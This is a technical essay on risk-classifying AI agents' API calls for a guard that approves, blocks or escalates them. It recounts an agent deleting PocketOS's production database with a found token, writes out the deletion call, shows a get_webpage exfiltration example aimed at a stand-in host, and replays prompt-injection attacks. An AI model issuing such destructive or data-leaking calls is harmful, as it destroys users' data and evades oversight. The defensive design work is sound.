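# Classifying API calls by risk when the guard does not know what the service does

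## What the guard sees and what it must decide

An AI agent is a program in which a language model works on a task by taking actions as well as writing text. It can search files, run commands, use login keys and contact other companies' software over the internet. Each piece of outside software is a service, such as one that processes payments, sends mail or rents out servers. A service takes requests from other programs through its application programming interface (API), a fixed set of operations with rules for using them. A call is one such request with its arguments filled in, such as a request to refund a particular payment or delete a particular disk.

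A guard is a component that checks each call an agent proposes before the call runs, and allows it, blocks it or refers it to a person. The decision is fairly easy when the guard's author knows the service well, but agents call many services that the author has never studied. The guard must then estimate the call's effect from only a method, an address or command, some arguments and a credential. A call's effect is everything it changes, reveals, spends or sets off if it succeeds, inside the service or beyond it.

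### The PocketOS deletion

PocketOS makes software that car rental companies use to manage reservations, payments and customer records. In April 2026, it kept its live database at Railway, a cloud hosting company, and its developers used Cursor, a coding agent, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'* reports that on 24 April the agent was working in PocketOS's staging environment, a test version of the software, when it ran into a problem with a credential. It found an API token, a string of characters that authorizes requests to a service, in a file unrelated to the task. It used the token to order Railway to delete the volume (Railway's unit of persistent storage) that held the live database.

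PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, wrote in a post that the deletion took about nine seconds, with no confirmation step (Leib, 2026, *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, ABC News). He also wrote that PocketOS had created the token only to add and remove custom domains and did not know it could delete storage (quoted on the software-failure site The Daily WTF).

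The backups disappeared along with the volume. Railway's documentation page *Backups* lists among its caveats that wiping a volume deletes all backups, but Crane said he had not known this. The newest copy PocketOS could find was three months old. Farrant (2026) reported in *An AI agent deleted a company’s entire database in 9 seconds* that the outage lasted more than 30 hours and that rental businesses lost access to their customer records and bookings. Tom's Hardware's *Claude-powered AI coding agent deletes entire company database in 9 seconds* (2026) reported that Crane spent hours helping the businesses piece bookings together from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

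PocketOS got its data back. Railway keeps separate off-site copies in case of hardware failure or natural disaster, and its chief executive, Jake Cooper, told ABC News that staff restored the database 30 minutes after they contacted Crane. Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* (Abdelwahab, 28 April), explained that the call had triggered a cascading delete, which removes an item and everything that depends on it, and that this made the backups look unavailable in Railway's interface. Early reports that the backups were permanently lost were therefore wrong, though PocketOS could not recover them itself.

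Abdelwahab also reported that a customer who deleted a volume in Railway's dashboard, the website for managing an account, had 48 hours to undo it, while deletions through the API had no such delay. Another customer had already encountered this difference on 13 April. In *Postgress volume lost*, antjanlaban (2026) reported deleting the wrong one of two volumes through the API, and a Railway employee replied that the recovery window covered only deletions made in the dashboard. After the PocketOS case, Railway gave API deletions the same 48-hour delay and postponed the removal of backups as well.

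When Crane asked the agent to explain itself, it wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. The Daily WTF objects that a language model cannot report its own reasons, because it composes a plausible answer from the text it is given. That seems right, so the explanation is weak evidence of why the agent made the call. But a guess would have been necessary anyway, because nothing in the request showed which environment the volume belonged to.

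### One call in three forms

Here is the call as a request in HTTP, the protocol that browsers and most web services use. Railway published the volume's identifier in shortened form.

```
POST /graphql/v2
Host: backboard.railway.app
Authorization: Bearer <token>

{"query": "mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: \"3d2c42fb-...\") }"}
```

POST is the HTTP method, a general verb at the head of the request. The last line is the body, written in GraphQL, a language in which the client specifies the operation it wants. A "mutation" is an operation that changes data. Railway's *Public API* gives a single address for every operation, and its example of a harmless request, which fetches the user's own name and email, is also a POST to that address. A guard has to parse the body to distinguish that request from the deletion of a production database, because both use the same method and address.

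Railway also supplies a command-line program, and there the same order is a subcommand:

```
railway volume delete --volume 3d2c42fb-... --yes
```

The `--yes` flag skips the confirmation question. According to Railway's reference for these commands, the command that deletes one file from a volume does not run when an AI agent invokes it, but the entry for deleting a whole volume does not mention this restriction.

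The third form uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface through which an AI application calls tools offered by separate servers. The application that runs the model and forwards its tool calls, such as Cursor, is the host. The server receives the tool call and does the work, often by sending an API request of its own. Glama, a directory of MCP servers, shows the code of a community-made tool, `volume_delete`, which takes one argument and sends Railway the same `volumeDelete` mutation. Sent over HTTP, and leaving out some routine fields, a call to such a tool looks like this:

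```
POST /mcp
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: volume_delete

{"method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "volume_delete",
            "arguments": {"volumeId": "3d2c42fb-..."}}}
```

The tool's name appears in both the body of the call and a header. Model Context Protocol (2026) added the header copy in its 28 July version so that a gateway between host and server can authorise calls without reading the body.

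| Field | HTTP request | Command | MCP tool call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Destination | Host and path, identical for all Railway operations | The program's name; the address is inside the program | The server that the host has connected to |
| Operation | POST, plus `volumeDelete` in the body | `volume delete` | `volume_delete` |
| Target | Volume identifier | Volume identifier or name | Volume identifier |
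| Credential | Token in a header | Usually a saved login, absent from the command | Often held by the server, absent from the arguments |
| Other clues | None | `--yes` | The tool's description and any annotations |

A guard can infer little from a credential, even when it is visible. Railway's project tokens, which reach only one environment, have their own header, but a token in the `Authorization: Bearer` header may give access to one workspace or to everything the customer owns. PocketOS's token gave access to everything the company owned on Railway.

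The agent in the PocketOS case mixed two of these forms. It used curl, a command-line program that sends HTTP requests, so a guard on its terminal would have received a command beginning with `curl` and had to extract the request from the arguments. A guard that watched only MCP tools would have missed the call. According to The Daily WTF, Cursor asks for approval before each call to a third-party MCP tool unless the user has exempted that tool, but this call did not go through MCP.

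### What the request leaves out

The name `volumeDelete` strongly suggests deletion, but the same request has had two different effects within one year. Until late April 2026 it destroyed the volume immediately, and since then it has scheduled the volume for removal after 48 hours. In *Detached volumes can't be deleted*, a customer, meirelon, reported in August that the call returned `true` while the volume stayed in the list. The customer repeated the deletion several times before Railway explained the delay. That month, Railway's *Manage Volumes with the Public API* still described the operation as permanent deletion and did not mention a waiting period. A guard that relied on this documentation would have overrated the danger. In April, a guard that had learned about deletion from the dashboard would have made the much worse mistake of underrating it.

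The guard also cannot tell from the request whose resource the target is. An identifier such as `3d2c42fb-...` does not show whether the resource is in production or staging, or whether it is a customer's data or a developer's scratch space. In the 13 April case, both volumes were attached at the same path, and a request to delete the right one would have differed only in the identifier. The guard could look up the identifier, but it would have to make another call to the service and know which call to make.

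The guard also cannot see whether the change can be undone. For a guard's purposes, a change is reversible if whoever made it can restore the earlier state with the access they already have. The PocketOS deletion was irreversible by this definition, even though the data was recovered, because only Railway could reach the off-site copies. Railway's code alone determined whether a deletion had a grace period.

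A call can also affect things that the request doesn't name. The PocketOS request named one volume, but not the backups or the rental companies' bookings. Other operations have less obvious effects. Railway's list of tools for its own MCP server includes `run-cloud-agent-task`, which can start a new agent for which Railway charges. It also includes `railway-agent`, which takes a request in plain English and passes it to a second AI agent to carry out in as many steps as it needs. To classify a call to `railway-agent`, the guard would have to predict the second agent's behaviour.

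Sometimes a single argument determines whether a call is destructive, even though the tool's name stays the same. Railway's local MCP server has a `remove_volume` tool, and for destructive operations the server first returns a preview and acts only on a call with `confirm: true`.

### What the call does and whether the user wants it

Abdelwahab reports that the request was authenticated, that Railway's API treated it like a request from any script with a valid token, and that nobody had told the agent to delete a database. A valid token does not show what the user wanted. Some readers accused Crane of giving the agent too much access, and Information Age, the Australian Computer Society's magazine, printed the reply, "Didn't give it access, it found it." Both sides have a point, because PocketOS left a powerful token within reach and nobody asked the agent to use it.

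A guard therefore has to decide both what a call does and whether the user authorised it. A drastic call may be authorised, as when meirelon wanted to delete a leftover volume of about 116 megabytes that still cost money. Reading a customer list changes nothing, but the user may still have good reason to forbid it. What a call does depends on the service, so the guard needs documentation, tests or past experience to judge its effects. To judge authorisation, it needs the user's instructions and the organisation's rules.

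A guard must decide both how risky a call is and whether it is authorised. Classifying calls by risk answers only the first question, but the second partly depends on it, because people can only approve what they understand. If a guard had asked a PocketOS developer whether to delete volume `3d2c42fb-...`, a developer who thought it was a staging volume might well have agreed.

### Three outcomes and two errors

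If the guard allows a call, the call goes to the service without a person reviewing it first. If the guard asks, the call waits until someone approves or refuses it. If the guard blocks the call, it never reaches the service, and the agent has to find another way or give up. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a person always be able to deny a tool call, and that applications show the user a tool's inputs before sending them.

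The guard can go wrong in two directions. A miss is a call that it should have stopped and let through. A false block is an acceptable call that it stopped. Each has a rate with its own denominator:

- miss rate = misses ÷ all calls that the guard should stop
- false-block rate = false blocks ÷ all acceptable calls

Suppose an agent makes 1,000 calls, 10 of which the guard should stop. The guard stops 8 of those 10, and also 50 of the 990 acceptable ones. Its miss rate is 20%. Its false-block rate is only about 5%, yet 50 of the 58 calls it stopped were acceptable. A user who sees mostly needless stops will be tempted to switch the guard off.

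Lowering one error rate with a crude rule usually raises the other. A guard that blocked every `volumeDelete` would have saved PocketOS's database and the one lost on 13 April, but it would also have stopped meirelon from deleting an unwanted disk. Asking a person to approve calls reduces this conflict but takes their time. That person may still approve a harmful call, and neither rate measures the burden of approving dozens of harmless ones.

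Four main methods help a guard to keep both errors down:

- An allowlist names calls or patterns that may run without further checks.
- A vendor declaration is a machine-readable statement by a service's supplier of what an operation does.
- A learned risk classifier is a trained or prompted model that judges whether a proposed call should run.
- A capability token is a credential that itself states and limits which operations its holder may perform, so that the service can refuse a call the guard has let through.

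## What methods and command names reveal about a call

A guard that knows nothing about a service can still read a call's HTTP method or command name. Both are useful clues because most developers choose methods and names that fit what an operation does. But the service's code determines the effect, and nothing forces that code to match the method or name.

### Safe and idempotent methods

*RFC 9110* (2022), the Internet Engineering Task Force's current standard for HTTP, defines a method as safe if the client "does not request, and does not expect, any state change" on the server. GET, which fetches a resource, is safe. So are HEAD, OPTIONS and TRACE, which return technical details about a resource or a connection.

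The definition of a safe method covers only what the client requests, so the server may do more. In one example from RFC 9110, most servers log each request, which could eventually fill the disk and crash the server. In another, a click on an advertisement sends a safe request that often charges the advertiser. The client did not ask for either effect, so the client is not accountable for them under the standard. That is a reasonable way to assign responsibility, but a guard has to predict the charge whoever is responsible.

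A method is idempotent if sending the same request several times has the same intended effect as sending it once. PUT and DELETE are idempotent, and so is every safe method. If a connection drops before the response arrives, a client can automatically repeat an idempotent request, but repeating a POST might make a second payment. Idempotent calls can still do great harm, since a single DELETE request can remove a whole database.

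POST tells a guard the least, because it asks the resource to process the body in whatever way that resource defines. Many services use POST for searches, since a long search fits badly into an address. Reschke, Snell and Bishop (2026), in *The HTTP QUERY Method*, give this example, shortened here:

```
POST /feed
q=foo&limit=10&sort=-published
```

"The HTTP QUERY Method" points out that nobody can recognise a search sent by POST as a harmless query without specific knowledge of the resource and the server. It defines a new method, QUERY, which carries a request body as POST does but is safe and idempotent by definition. The IETF published the specification as a Proposed Standard in June 2026. In September, InfoQ (2026) reported that the Rust language's `http` library had added support and that other tools were tracking the change, but expected adoption to take years. Guards will therefore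 still encounter searches sent by POST.

| Method | What the client requests | Safe | Idempotent |
|---|---|---|---|
| GET | Fetch a resource | Yes | Yes |
| QUERY | Run the query in the body | Yes | Yes |
| PUT | Create or replace a resource | No | Yes |
| DELETE | Remove a resource | No | Yes |
| PATCH | Change part of a resource | No | Not guaranteed |
| POST | Process the body as the resource defines | Not guaranteed | Not guaranteed |

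A server can break the rule for QUERY, just as it can for GET. Even a server that follows the rule may create a new address where the client can fetch the results again, and Reschke and colleagues warn against putting sensitive parts of the query in that address.

### The Google Web Accelerator

In May 2005, Google released a test version of Web Accelerator, a program that fetched linked pages before the user clicked, so that they would open faster. It ran on the user's computer, so it could also see pages behind a login. Two days later, the software company 37signals explained in *Google Web Accelerator* (2005), a post on its blog Signal v. Noise, why users' pages had been disappearing from Backpack, its online organiser. The accelerator was following links such as "delete this" as if they led to ordinary pages. Confirmation questions written in JavaScript gave no protection, because the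 accelerator ignored them.

Hicks (2005) reports in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security* that Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, also spoke of deleted accounts. Fried said that only a few users had complained and that the company blocked the accelerator within 30 minutes of finding the cause. Some of the blog's readers could not get the accelerator to delete anything in their own tests, but another reported losing important sales leads from a company database.

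Marissa Mayer, Google's director of consumer web products, told Hicks that the accelerator skipped links with a question mark, which usually introduces parameters. She expected a link that deleted something to contain one, but conceded that this assumption might be wrong. That October, *Google Web Accelerator* (Deaton, 2005) quoted a description of the product, according to which it also skipped encrypted pages. The accelerator therefore worked much like a simple guard, judging unfamiliar requests by their method and address. The question-mark rule fails when a site puts the action in the path, as in `/delete/socks`.

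The argument that followed was mostly about the words "SHOULD NOT" in the HTTP standard in force at the time. That standard, *Hypertext Transfer Protocol* by Fielding and colleagues, stated that GET "SHOULD NOT" mean taking an action other than retrieval. David Heinemeier Hansson, a partner at 37signals, argued in the comments on the company's post that this was a recommendation which developers could set aside for good reasons. Many developers thought a login was a good enough reason, because automated programs had never got past one before. *Fighting RFCs with RFCs* (Willison, 2005) supported Hansson's reading with the IETF's own glossary, under which "SHOULD NOT" leaves room for "valid reasons in particular circumstances".

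The other side blamed the websites. Sivonen (2005) wrote on a web standards mailing list that the applications using GET for unsafe operations were broken, not the accelerator. Willison soon changed his mind, after readers pointed out that a login does not protect such links. A malicious page can make a logged-in user's browser request the link, an attack called cross-site request forgery. *Google Web Accelerator Debate* (2006), a blog post by the *HTTP Developer's Handbook* author, took up this point. It argued that every dangerous link its author had seen cited either had a query string, so the accelerator would have skipped it, or was already open to forged requests. Even Fried acknowledged to Hicks that deletions should technically use buttons instead of links.

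I think the critics were right about the standard, since the glossary also requires anyone who departs from a recommendation to understand the full implications first. The IETF's *Safe Methods* section had used "should never" in an earlier version, but the version still in force in 2005 had softened this to "SHOULD NOT". The IETF has since tightened the wording, and under RFC 9110, if an address such as `page?do=delete` performs an unsafe action, its owner "MUST" disable that action for safe methods.

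But Heinemeier Hansson was right that a program would meet services that break the standard. As he put it, "Having a standard is not an excuse for not looking out the windows." A stricter rule makes it clearer who is at fault after a deletion, but it does not help a guard work out which services obey it.

### How often GET works in place of POST

In *When POST Becomes GET*, Golinelli, Hannachi and Crispo (2026) measured how strictly websites separate GET and POST. They used an automated browser to visit the top 10,000 sites in the Tranco popularity ranking without logging in. On each site, the browser opened up to 10 pages, filled in forms with harmless values and clicked some buttons, and their software recorded every resulting POST request.

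The software then moved the parameters of each POST from the body into the URL and sent the result as a GET. It also sent a GET with no parameters, as a control. The researchers counted a request as interchangeable only if the rewritten GET produced a response equivalent to the original response and the control did not. Without the control, they would also have counted requests to pages that return the same thing whatever the client sends.

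They captured POST requests on 3,200 sites and could replay at least one on 2,734 of them. The replayed requests covered 8,291 distinct routes, where a route is roughly one address combined with one body format. On 646 routes (7.8%) across 407 sites, the GET version got an equivalent response. A further 1,782 individual requests were ambiguous because the control also matched.

Web frameworks help explain the result. In plain PHP, for example, a developer can read parameters from the address and the body through a single variable, and the same script handles both methods unless the developer adds a check. Other frameworks keep the two sources separate or accept only the method the developer names.

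Two requests can get matching responses without having the same effect on the server. Golinelli and colleagues compared HTML pages only by their sequence of tags, so a page reporting a saved change could match one reporting an error. They manually reviewed 30 positive cases and found the responses equivalent in all of them, which supports their comparison of responses, but they did not check whether anything had changed on the servers. They would also have counted a GET as not interchangeable if it carried out the operation but returned a page with a different structure.

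The sample also leaves out most risky calls. To avoid damaging live sites, the researchers dropped requests whose paths contained words suggesting a destructive or state-changing action, and they collected none from behind a login. The largest group of interchangeable requests, 31%, looked like searches or filters, for which accepting both methods may be intentional. The study covers requests that web pages send, while agents mostly call documented APIs with a key. The 7.8% figure is therefore not an estimate of how often a GET request changes something.

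Many sites protect POST requests against forgery by requiring a secret value. In a smaller but more directly relevant test, Golinelli and colleagues examined 115 interchangeable requests that included such a value. For seven of them, on two sites, the server rejected a wrong value sent by POST but accepted it by GET. A guard that inspects POST requests but allows GET requests unchecked could be bypassed the same way.

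### When the method is misleading

Some services document a GET that acts. Telegram's manual for its Bot API, which lets programs send chat messages, states that the API supports both GET and POST. This request therefore sends a message:

```
GET /bot<token>/sendMessage?chat_id=42&text=Hello
```

If the text were a list of customers, the call would be a disclosure, meaning information reaches someone outside the trusted group and no later call can take it back. The IETF advises designers of HTTP applications that a GET should have no significant side effects, partly because client software retries GETs that fail. A retry here could send the message twice.

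POST misleads in the opposite direction. Elasticsearch, a widely used search engine, accepts searches like this one:

```
POST /orders/_search
{"query": {"match": {"status": "cancelled"}}}
```

A guard that blocked every POST request would block a search for cancelled orders sent as a POST. But if the path ended in `_delete_by_query`, a request with the same method and body would delete every order the search finds. Only the path distinguishes the read from the mass deletion.

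The PocketOS request showed that with GraphQL even the path doesn't help a guard classify a call, because one address serves every operation. According to Golinelli and colleagues, the draft rules for GraphQL over HTTP say that servers may accept read-only queries by GET but must not execute mutations that way. If the server follows the draft, a GET is therefore good evidence of a read, while a POST could be a query or a mutation.

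JSON-RPC, a simple format for calling functions on another computer, names the function in a body field called `method`, which is unrelated to the HTTP method. Programs that use the Ethereum blockchain send `eth_getBalance` to look up a balance and `eth_sendRawTransaction` to submit a signed payment, and both can go by POST to the same address. A client can also put several calls into one request as a list, so a guard that read only the first item could approve a balance check and let through the payment behind it.

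### When a command depends on its arguments

GitHub's command-line program, `gh`, has a subcommand for sending any request to GitHub's API. Its manual explains that `gh api` uses GET by default and switches to POST when the user adds parameters, unless the user names a method. Compare three commands:

```
gh api repos/acme/shop/issues
gh api repos/acme/shop/issues -f title="Broken link"
gh api -X GET repos/acme/shop/issues -f state=closed
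```

The first command lists the open issues in a project, the second creates a new issue, and the third lists the closed ones. None of them contains the word POST. A guard that allowed every command beginning with `gh api repos/` as a read would let the second through, and a guard that stopped every `-f` would needlessly stop the third, which only reads. In `curl`, which the PocketOS agent used, `--data` similarly turns the request into a POST, and adding `--get` turns it back into a GET.

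Database commands have the same problem. SELECT is the SQL command for reading data, but it can also call functions. In the database system PostgreSQL, `SELECT pg_terminate_backend(4711)` ends another user's session. Developers can also write their own functions, and according to PostgreSQL's manual, a function in the default category may do anything, including modify the database. A guard that sees `SELECT archive_customer(42)` can guess from the name that the function changes something, but it would have no such hint if the developer had named the function `customer_status`.

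Flags can matter more than the command's name. `rsync -a photos/ backup/` copies new and changed files from one folder to another. Adding `--delete` also removes every file in `backup/` that is missing from `photos/`. If `photos/` is empty, perhaps because a disk did not connect, the command empties the backup. Another flag, `--remove-source-files`, deletes the original files from `photos/` once rsync has transferred them.

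### When the name is accurate but incomplete

Even when the guard correctly identifies a call as a read or a write, it can misjudge the call's risk.

`aws secretsmanager get-secret-value` only gets a value, but that value may be the password of a production database, and the command prints it where the agent can read it. The password then becomes part of the language model's input, and the agent may copy it into a file, a message or a later request. The command doesn't change the stored data, but the company may have to replace the password.

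Reading can also cost money. Under one pricing plan for BigQuery, Google's service for analysing large datasets, customers pay for the amount of data each query processes. Google warns in its documentation that adding `LIMIT 10` to a query generally doesn't reduce the amount of data read, so a request for ten rows can cost as much as a request for the whole table.

Small writes can have large consequences because other systems react to them. According to GitHub's API documentation, creating an issue triggers notifications, so the second `gh api` command above may send email to everyone who follows the project. Project owners can also define workflows, which are scripts that run after events such as a new commit, and many projects use them to publish their software. In such a project, a PUT request that corrects a typo in a text file could release a new version to customers.

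Whether a change on GitHub starts a workflow may depend on the credential used to make it. Changes made with the temporary token that GitHub issues to a running workflow do not normally start further workflows, which prevents endless loops, but the same changes made with a developer's personal token do. Two requests with the same method, address and body can therefore have different effects.

### What parsing the body recovers

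Parsing resolves many of these cases. A guard can parse a GraphQL body to find out whether the operation is a query or a mutation, which fields it calls and with what arguments. It can also extract the function name of every call in a JSON-RPC list, and the type of an SQL statement and the functions inside it. To parse a command line, the guard has to apply the program's own rules, such as the switch from GET to POST in `gh api`. Parsing would have been enough to recognise the PocketOS request as a deletion.

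The guard has to parse the parts of a call that the server acts on. In GraphQL, the client can give an operation any name, so a guard that logged or judged `mutation GetStatus { volumeDelete(...) }` as "GetStatus" would miss the deletion.

Sometimes the body does not contain the operation. Some GraphQL servers store queries in advance and let the client send only a short code that identifies one, so the guard needs the server's list. A `curl` command can take its body from a file, so the guard has to open that file and make sure it doesn't change before the command runs. The guard may also not recognize the body's format. Golinelli and colleagues built converters for the three most common body formats and still skipped 5,641 of the 21,280 POST requests they captured (26.5%) because the format was unknown or unsupported. Even a guard that supports more formats should expect some bodies that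 it cannot read.

Even perfect parsing of a request does not reveal information stored elsewhere, such as the code of a database function, the size of a table, the workflows that a commit triggers, or the importance of the target. Names are therefore better evidence of danger than of safety. Developers seldom call an operation "delete" if it deletes nothing, but many operations with mild names change, reveal or spend something.

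The table shows where a guard would have to look to correct its first guess in each case.

| Surface form | Likely guess | Actual effect | Where the difference lies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Telegram: `GET .../sendMessage?...` | Read | Sends a message | Path |
| Elasticsearch: `POST /orders/_search` | Write | Searches orders | Path |
| GraphQL: `POST /graphql/v2` | Write | Reads or changes data | Operation in the body |
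| Ethereum: POST to a node | Same as the previous call | Looks up a balance or submits a payment | `method` field in the body |
| `gh api .../issues -f title=...` | Read | Creates an issue and may notify people | Arguments |
| `SELECT archive_customer(42)` | Read | Whatever the function does | Code stored in the database |
| `rsync -a --delete photos/ backup/` | Copy | Copies files and deletes others | Flag |
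| `aws secretsmanager get-secret-value` | Harmless read | Reveals a secret to the agent | Sensitivity of the value |
| BigQuery: `SELECT * ... LIMIT 10` | Cheap read | May cost as much as reading the whole table | Table size and pricing plan |
| GitHub: `PUT .../contents/README.md` | Small edit | May publish a new version | Workflows and credential |

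## Choosing the risk classes

After parsing a call, the guard assigns it a risk class and bases its decision on that class. The simplest scheme divides calls into reads, which the guard allows, and writes, which it asks a person about.

### Why read and write are not enough

Some reads expose a password or run up a bill, like the AWS and BigQuery commands above. A read can also carry data out. In *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026), the researchers sorted the 69 tools of AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents work with simulated mail, calendar, file, chat, travel and banking services while attackers plant instructions in the data. They counted 44 tools as local reads, which only look up the user's own data, and 24 as writes or outward actions. The remaining tool, `get_webpage`, fetches a page, but the agent chooses the address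 and can put private data in it:

```
get_webpage(url="https://example.net/?note=card+ends+4417")
```

Whoever runs `example.net` can find the note in the server's log. The researchers' guard checks `get_webpage` but allows local reads without further checks. Their reasoning is that a read does no harm until the agent writes or sends something.

The write class is also too broad because it covers saving a draft, paying an invoice and deleting a database. A guard that stops all three will often interrupt the user over trivial changes.

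In January 2025, the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) gathered about 140 experts to discuss how to classify agents' tools. They came up with seven approaches but did not settle on one. The approaches included sorting tools by function, by severity and reversibility of harm, and by how easily people can monitor them. NIST's *Lessons Learned from the Consortium* offers a grid with read-only, constrained write and unconstrained write on one axis, and trusted and untrusted environments on the other. An agent that only reads the open web counts as read-only in an untrusted environment.

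### Six properties of a call

A guard's author can describe most of what matters about a call with six properties:

- Change of state: whether the call alters anything the service stores.
- Reversibility: whether the party that made the call can undo it without help.
- Disclosure: whether information reaches someone outside the trusted group.
- Reach: how many people, records or systems the call affects. Deleting one meeting and deleting a recurring series may differ by a single argument.
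- Cost: the money, computing time or quota the call uses up.
- Change of access rights: whether the call gives someone lasting power to make calls of their own, for example by sharing a folder or creating a token.

Cost is hard to judge one call at a time. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) describes an agent with a travel budget of 1,500 euros that books a 900-euro flight and a 700-euro hotel in parallel. Each booking is affordable by itself, but together they exceed the budget, and the agent can cancel the hotel but not the flight. A guard would need to keep a running total of spending to catch this.

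Disclosing information can have effects that remain after the call appears to have been undone. In another of their examples, a supplier acts on an agent's offer and may already have bought materials by the time the agent withdraws it.

### Why one scale does not fit

Trofimov and Novikov show that even simple operations can't all be ranked on one scale from harmless to dangerous. Two operations commute if their order doesn't affect the result. Adding 5 to a stock count commutes with adding 3, but it is not idempotent, because an agent that sends "add 5" twice adds 10. Deleting a file is idempotent, since a second deletion changes nothing, but it doesn't commute with writing the file, because the file remains only if the write comes last. The increment is therefore riskier when an agent retries after a network failure, and the deletion is riskier when two agents work on the same file.

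Retries are a problem because an agent whose request times out cannot tell whether the service carried it out. Li (2026), in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*, tested nine recent models on six simulated services. When the service had done the work and only the reply was lost, the strongest models checked first, so they repeated the write in only 0.5% of runs. When the request was still on its way, checking revealed nothing, and the same models duplicated the write in 56% of runs. Letting every write carry an idempotency key, a string by which the service recognises a repeated request, cut the duplicate rate from 28% to 4%. In Li's billing service, a refund could be repeated safely without a key, but a charge could not. A guard that labels both as "payment" would miss this difference.

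The published scales also differ on which effects are worse, for example on whether a call that permanently deletes a user's file is worse than one that emails an outsider.

*Beyond Attack-Success Rate* (Owiredu-Ashley, 2026) grades attacks on a seven-level scale, L0 to L6, by reversibility, reach and change of privilege. It ranks an effect on another party above a permanent loss to the user alone, so the email gets L4 and the deletion L3. *Do I Need the Cloud?* (Younesi, 2026) uses four tiers and reverses the order, putting the deletion in the highest tier and the email in the second-highest. *Small agents should know what their tools do* (Kovalenko and Redchych, 2026) classes both as "destructive", including the email because the sender cannot make recipients forget what they have read.

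All three rankings are defensible. The email is riskier than the deletion for a clinic with hourly backups, but the deletion is riskier for a photographer who has only one copy of a wedding's photos. The guard's author should therefore record the properties separately and choose a rule for combining them. Kovalenko and Redchych do this in part by giving each tool one of four effects (pure, read, write or destructive) and a separate flag for idempotence. For example, moving a meeting and cancelling an order are both idempotent, although the first is a write and the second is destructive.

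### The Reversibility Classes

*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 17 November 2026) orders calls mainly by reversibility. It treats disclosure as irreversible and most changes to access rights as hard to recover from.

| Class | Name | When it applies | Suggested policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | No effect | Nothing changes outside the agent | Act |
| R1 | Restorable | The acting party can restore the exact earlier state | Act, then notify |
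| R2 | Compensable | A known further action reaches an acceptable equivalent at a limited cost | Ask, or use a budget approved in advance |
| R3 | Hard to recover | Recovery needs a person, an outside process or unlimited effort; also changes to access, credentials, availability or physical state | Ask each time |
| R4 | Irreversible | Disclosure, permanent destruction or another effect that nobody can recall or compensate for | Never act without approval |

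A call qualifies for R1 only if it meets three conditions:

1. A complete record of the earlier state exists, either in an accessible version history or in a copy made before the call.
2. The acting party can write that state back without help from anyone else.
3. Nobody outside has seen, received or acted on the changed state.

The PocketOS deletion did not meet the second condition. With hindsight it belongs in R3, but a guard that did not know about Railway's off-site copies would have had to assume R4.

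Each tool starts with a base class that reflects its broadest effect, and rules can assign a lower class to calls with particular arguments. The classifier tries the rules in order and applies the first that matches. If an argument is missing or unfamiliar, the call keeps the base class unless a rule covers that case. Waghmare and Sufi want each rule that lowers the class to match a narrow form known to be harmless, rather than any call that lacks a dangerous word. For example, beginning with SELECT is not enough to give a database command a lower class.

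A call that the classifier does not recognise gets R4, unless the guard relies on the supplier's MCP hints about the tool. This default prevents misses but causes many interruptions, because a weather lookup on an unfamiliar service gets the same class as a mass deletion.

Whoever deploys the guard can override a class if they document the reason, but they cannot lower the class of a disclosure. For example, they can classify an edit to a private file as R1 if the deployment saves a copy of the file first. If the copy fails, the edit returns to its original class. The deployment has to make and restore the copy, and the classifier only checks for confirmation that it exists.

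### How far the labels agree

Waghmare and Sufi drafted labels for 536 tools on 20 MCP servers with help from AI. They put 333 tools in R0 (62.1%), 31 in R1 (5.8%), 18 in R2 (3.4%), 39 in R3 (7.3%) and 115 in R4 (21.5%). By default, their program asks a person about R2 and above, so going by these base labels alone, it differs from a read/write rule only on the 31 tools in R1. The three middle classes make most of the scheme's finer distinctions but hold only 88 tools.

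They then translated the hints that MCP servers attach to tools, such as "read-only" or "destructive", into risk classes and compared these with their own labels. Of the 481 tools they could compare, 118 (24.5%) had a different class under the hints, higher for 85 and lower for 33. For 61 tools, relying on the hints would have changed whether the guard asked, removing the question for 20 and adding it for 41. Ten tools labeled irreversible in the registry had a read-only hint. Part of the disagreement comes from the translation, because no combination of hints translates to R2.

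In a separate review, Sufi considered 150 of the tools and rated 148, leaving two undecided for lack of evidence. His rating matched the registry for 75 (50.7%), was higher for 67 and lower for six. The match rate measures agreement rather than accuracy, because nobody had established the correct labels. Sufi is also a co-author of the scheme, and for 139 of the ratings he approved batches of suggestions from an AI system. At least one suggestion was plainly mistaken, because it put a browser search tool in R0 and overlooked an option that writes the results to a file.

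The sample also lowered the match rate because it included every R1 and R2 tool in the registry, and those were the hardest to agree on. Sufi's ratings matched 28 of 34 tools in R0 and 30 of 34 in R4, but only one of 31 in R1. If the sample had reflected how common each class is in the registry, the match rate would have been about 74%. The "restorable" label is fragile, because on a second look Sufi moved nearly every R1 tool to a higher class.

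The classifier passed all 738 of its rule checks. Waghmare and Sufi derived the expected answers from the same rules, so the checks show that the program follows the rules, but not whether the rules are right.

### Replaying recorded attacks

Waghmare and Sufi also ran their guard over 2,158 recorded agent runs to see where it would have stopped to ask. The runs came from AgentDojo and from τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service for an airline, a shop and a telephone company. All the runs used Claude 3.7 Sonnet, an old model by late 2026. An attacker had planted instructions in 949 of the runs, and the attack succeeded in 47 of those. Waghmare and Sufi could link 29 of the successful attacks to a particular call.

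The tested version tracks the session. Once the agent has read data, any call that could send data out rises to R4, unless every destination is on an allowlist.

| Rule | Attack calls stopped, of 29 | Approval requests in 1,209 harmless runs |
|---|---|---|
| Ask only about the most severe calls | 9 | 1,087 |
| Ask about every write | 18 | 1,895 |
| Session-aware guard | 29 | 1,904 |

With risk classes, the guard stopped 11 more attack calls than the read/write rule did and asked nine more questions. All 11 calls came from AgentDojo's chat tasks, and the guard stopped them only because it treated a web visit as a way to send data out. When Waghmare and Sufi counted web visits as ordinary reads, the guard stopped 18 attack calls, the same number as the read/write rule. The improvement came from recognising that a fetch such as `get_webpage` can disclose data, and a read/write rule with that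 one exception might do as well.

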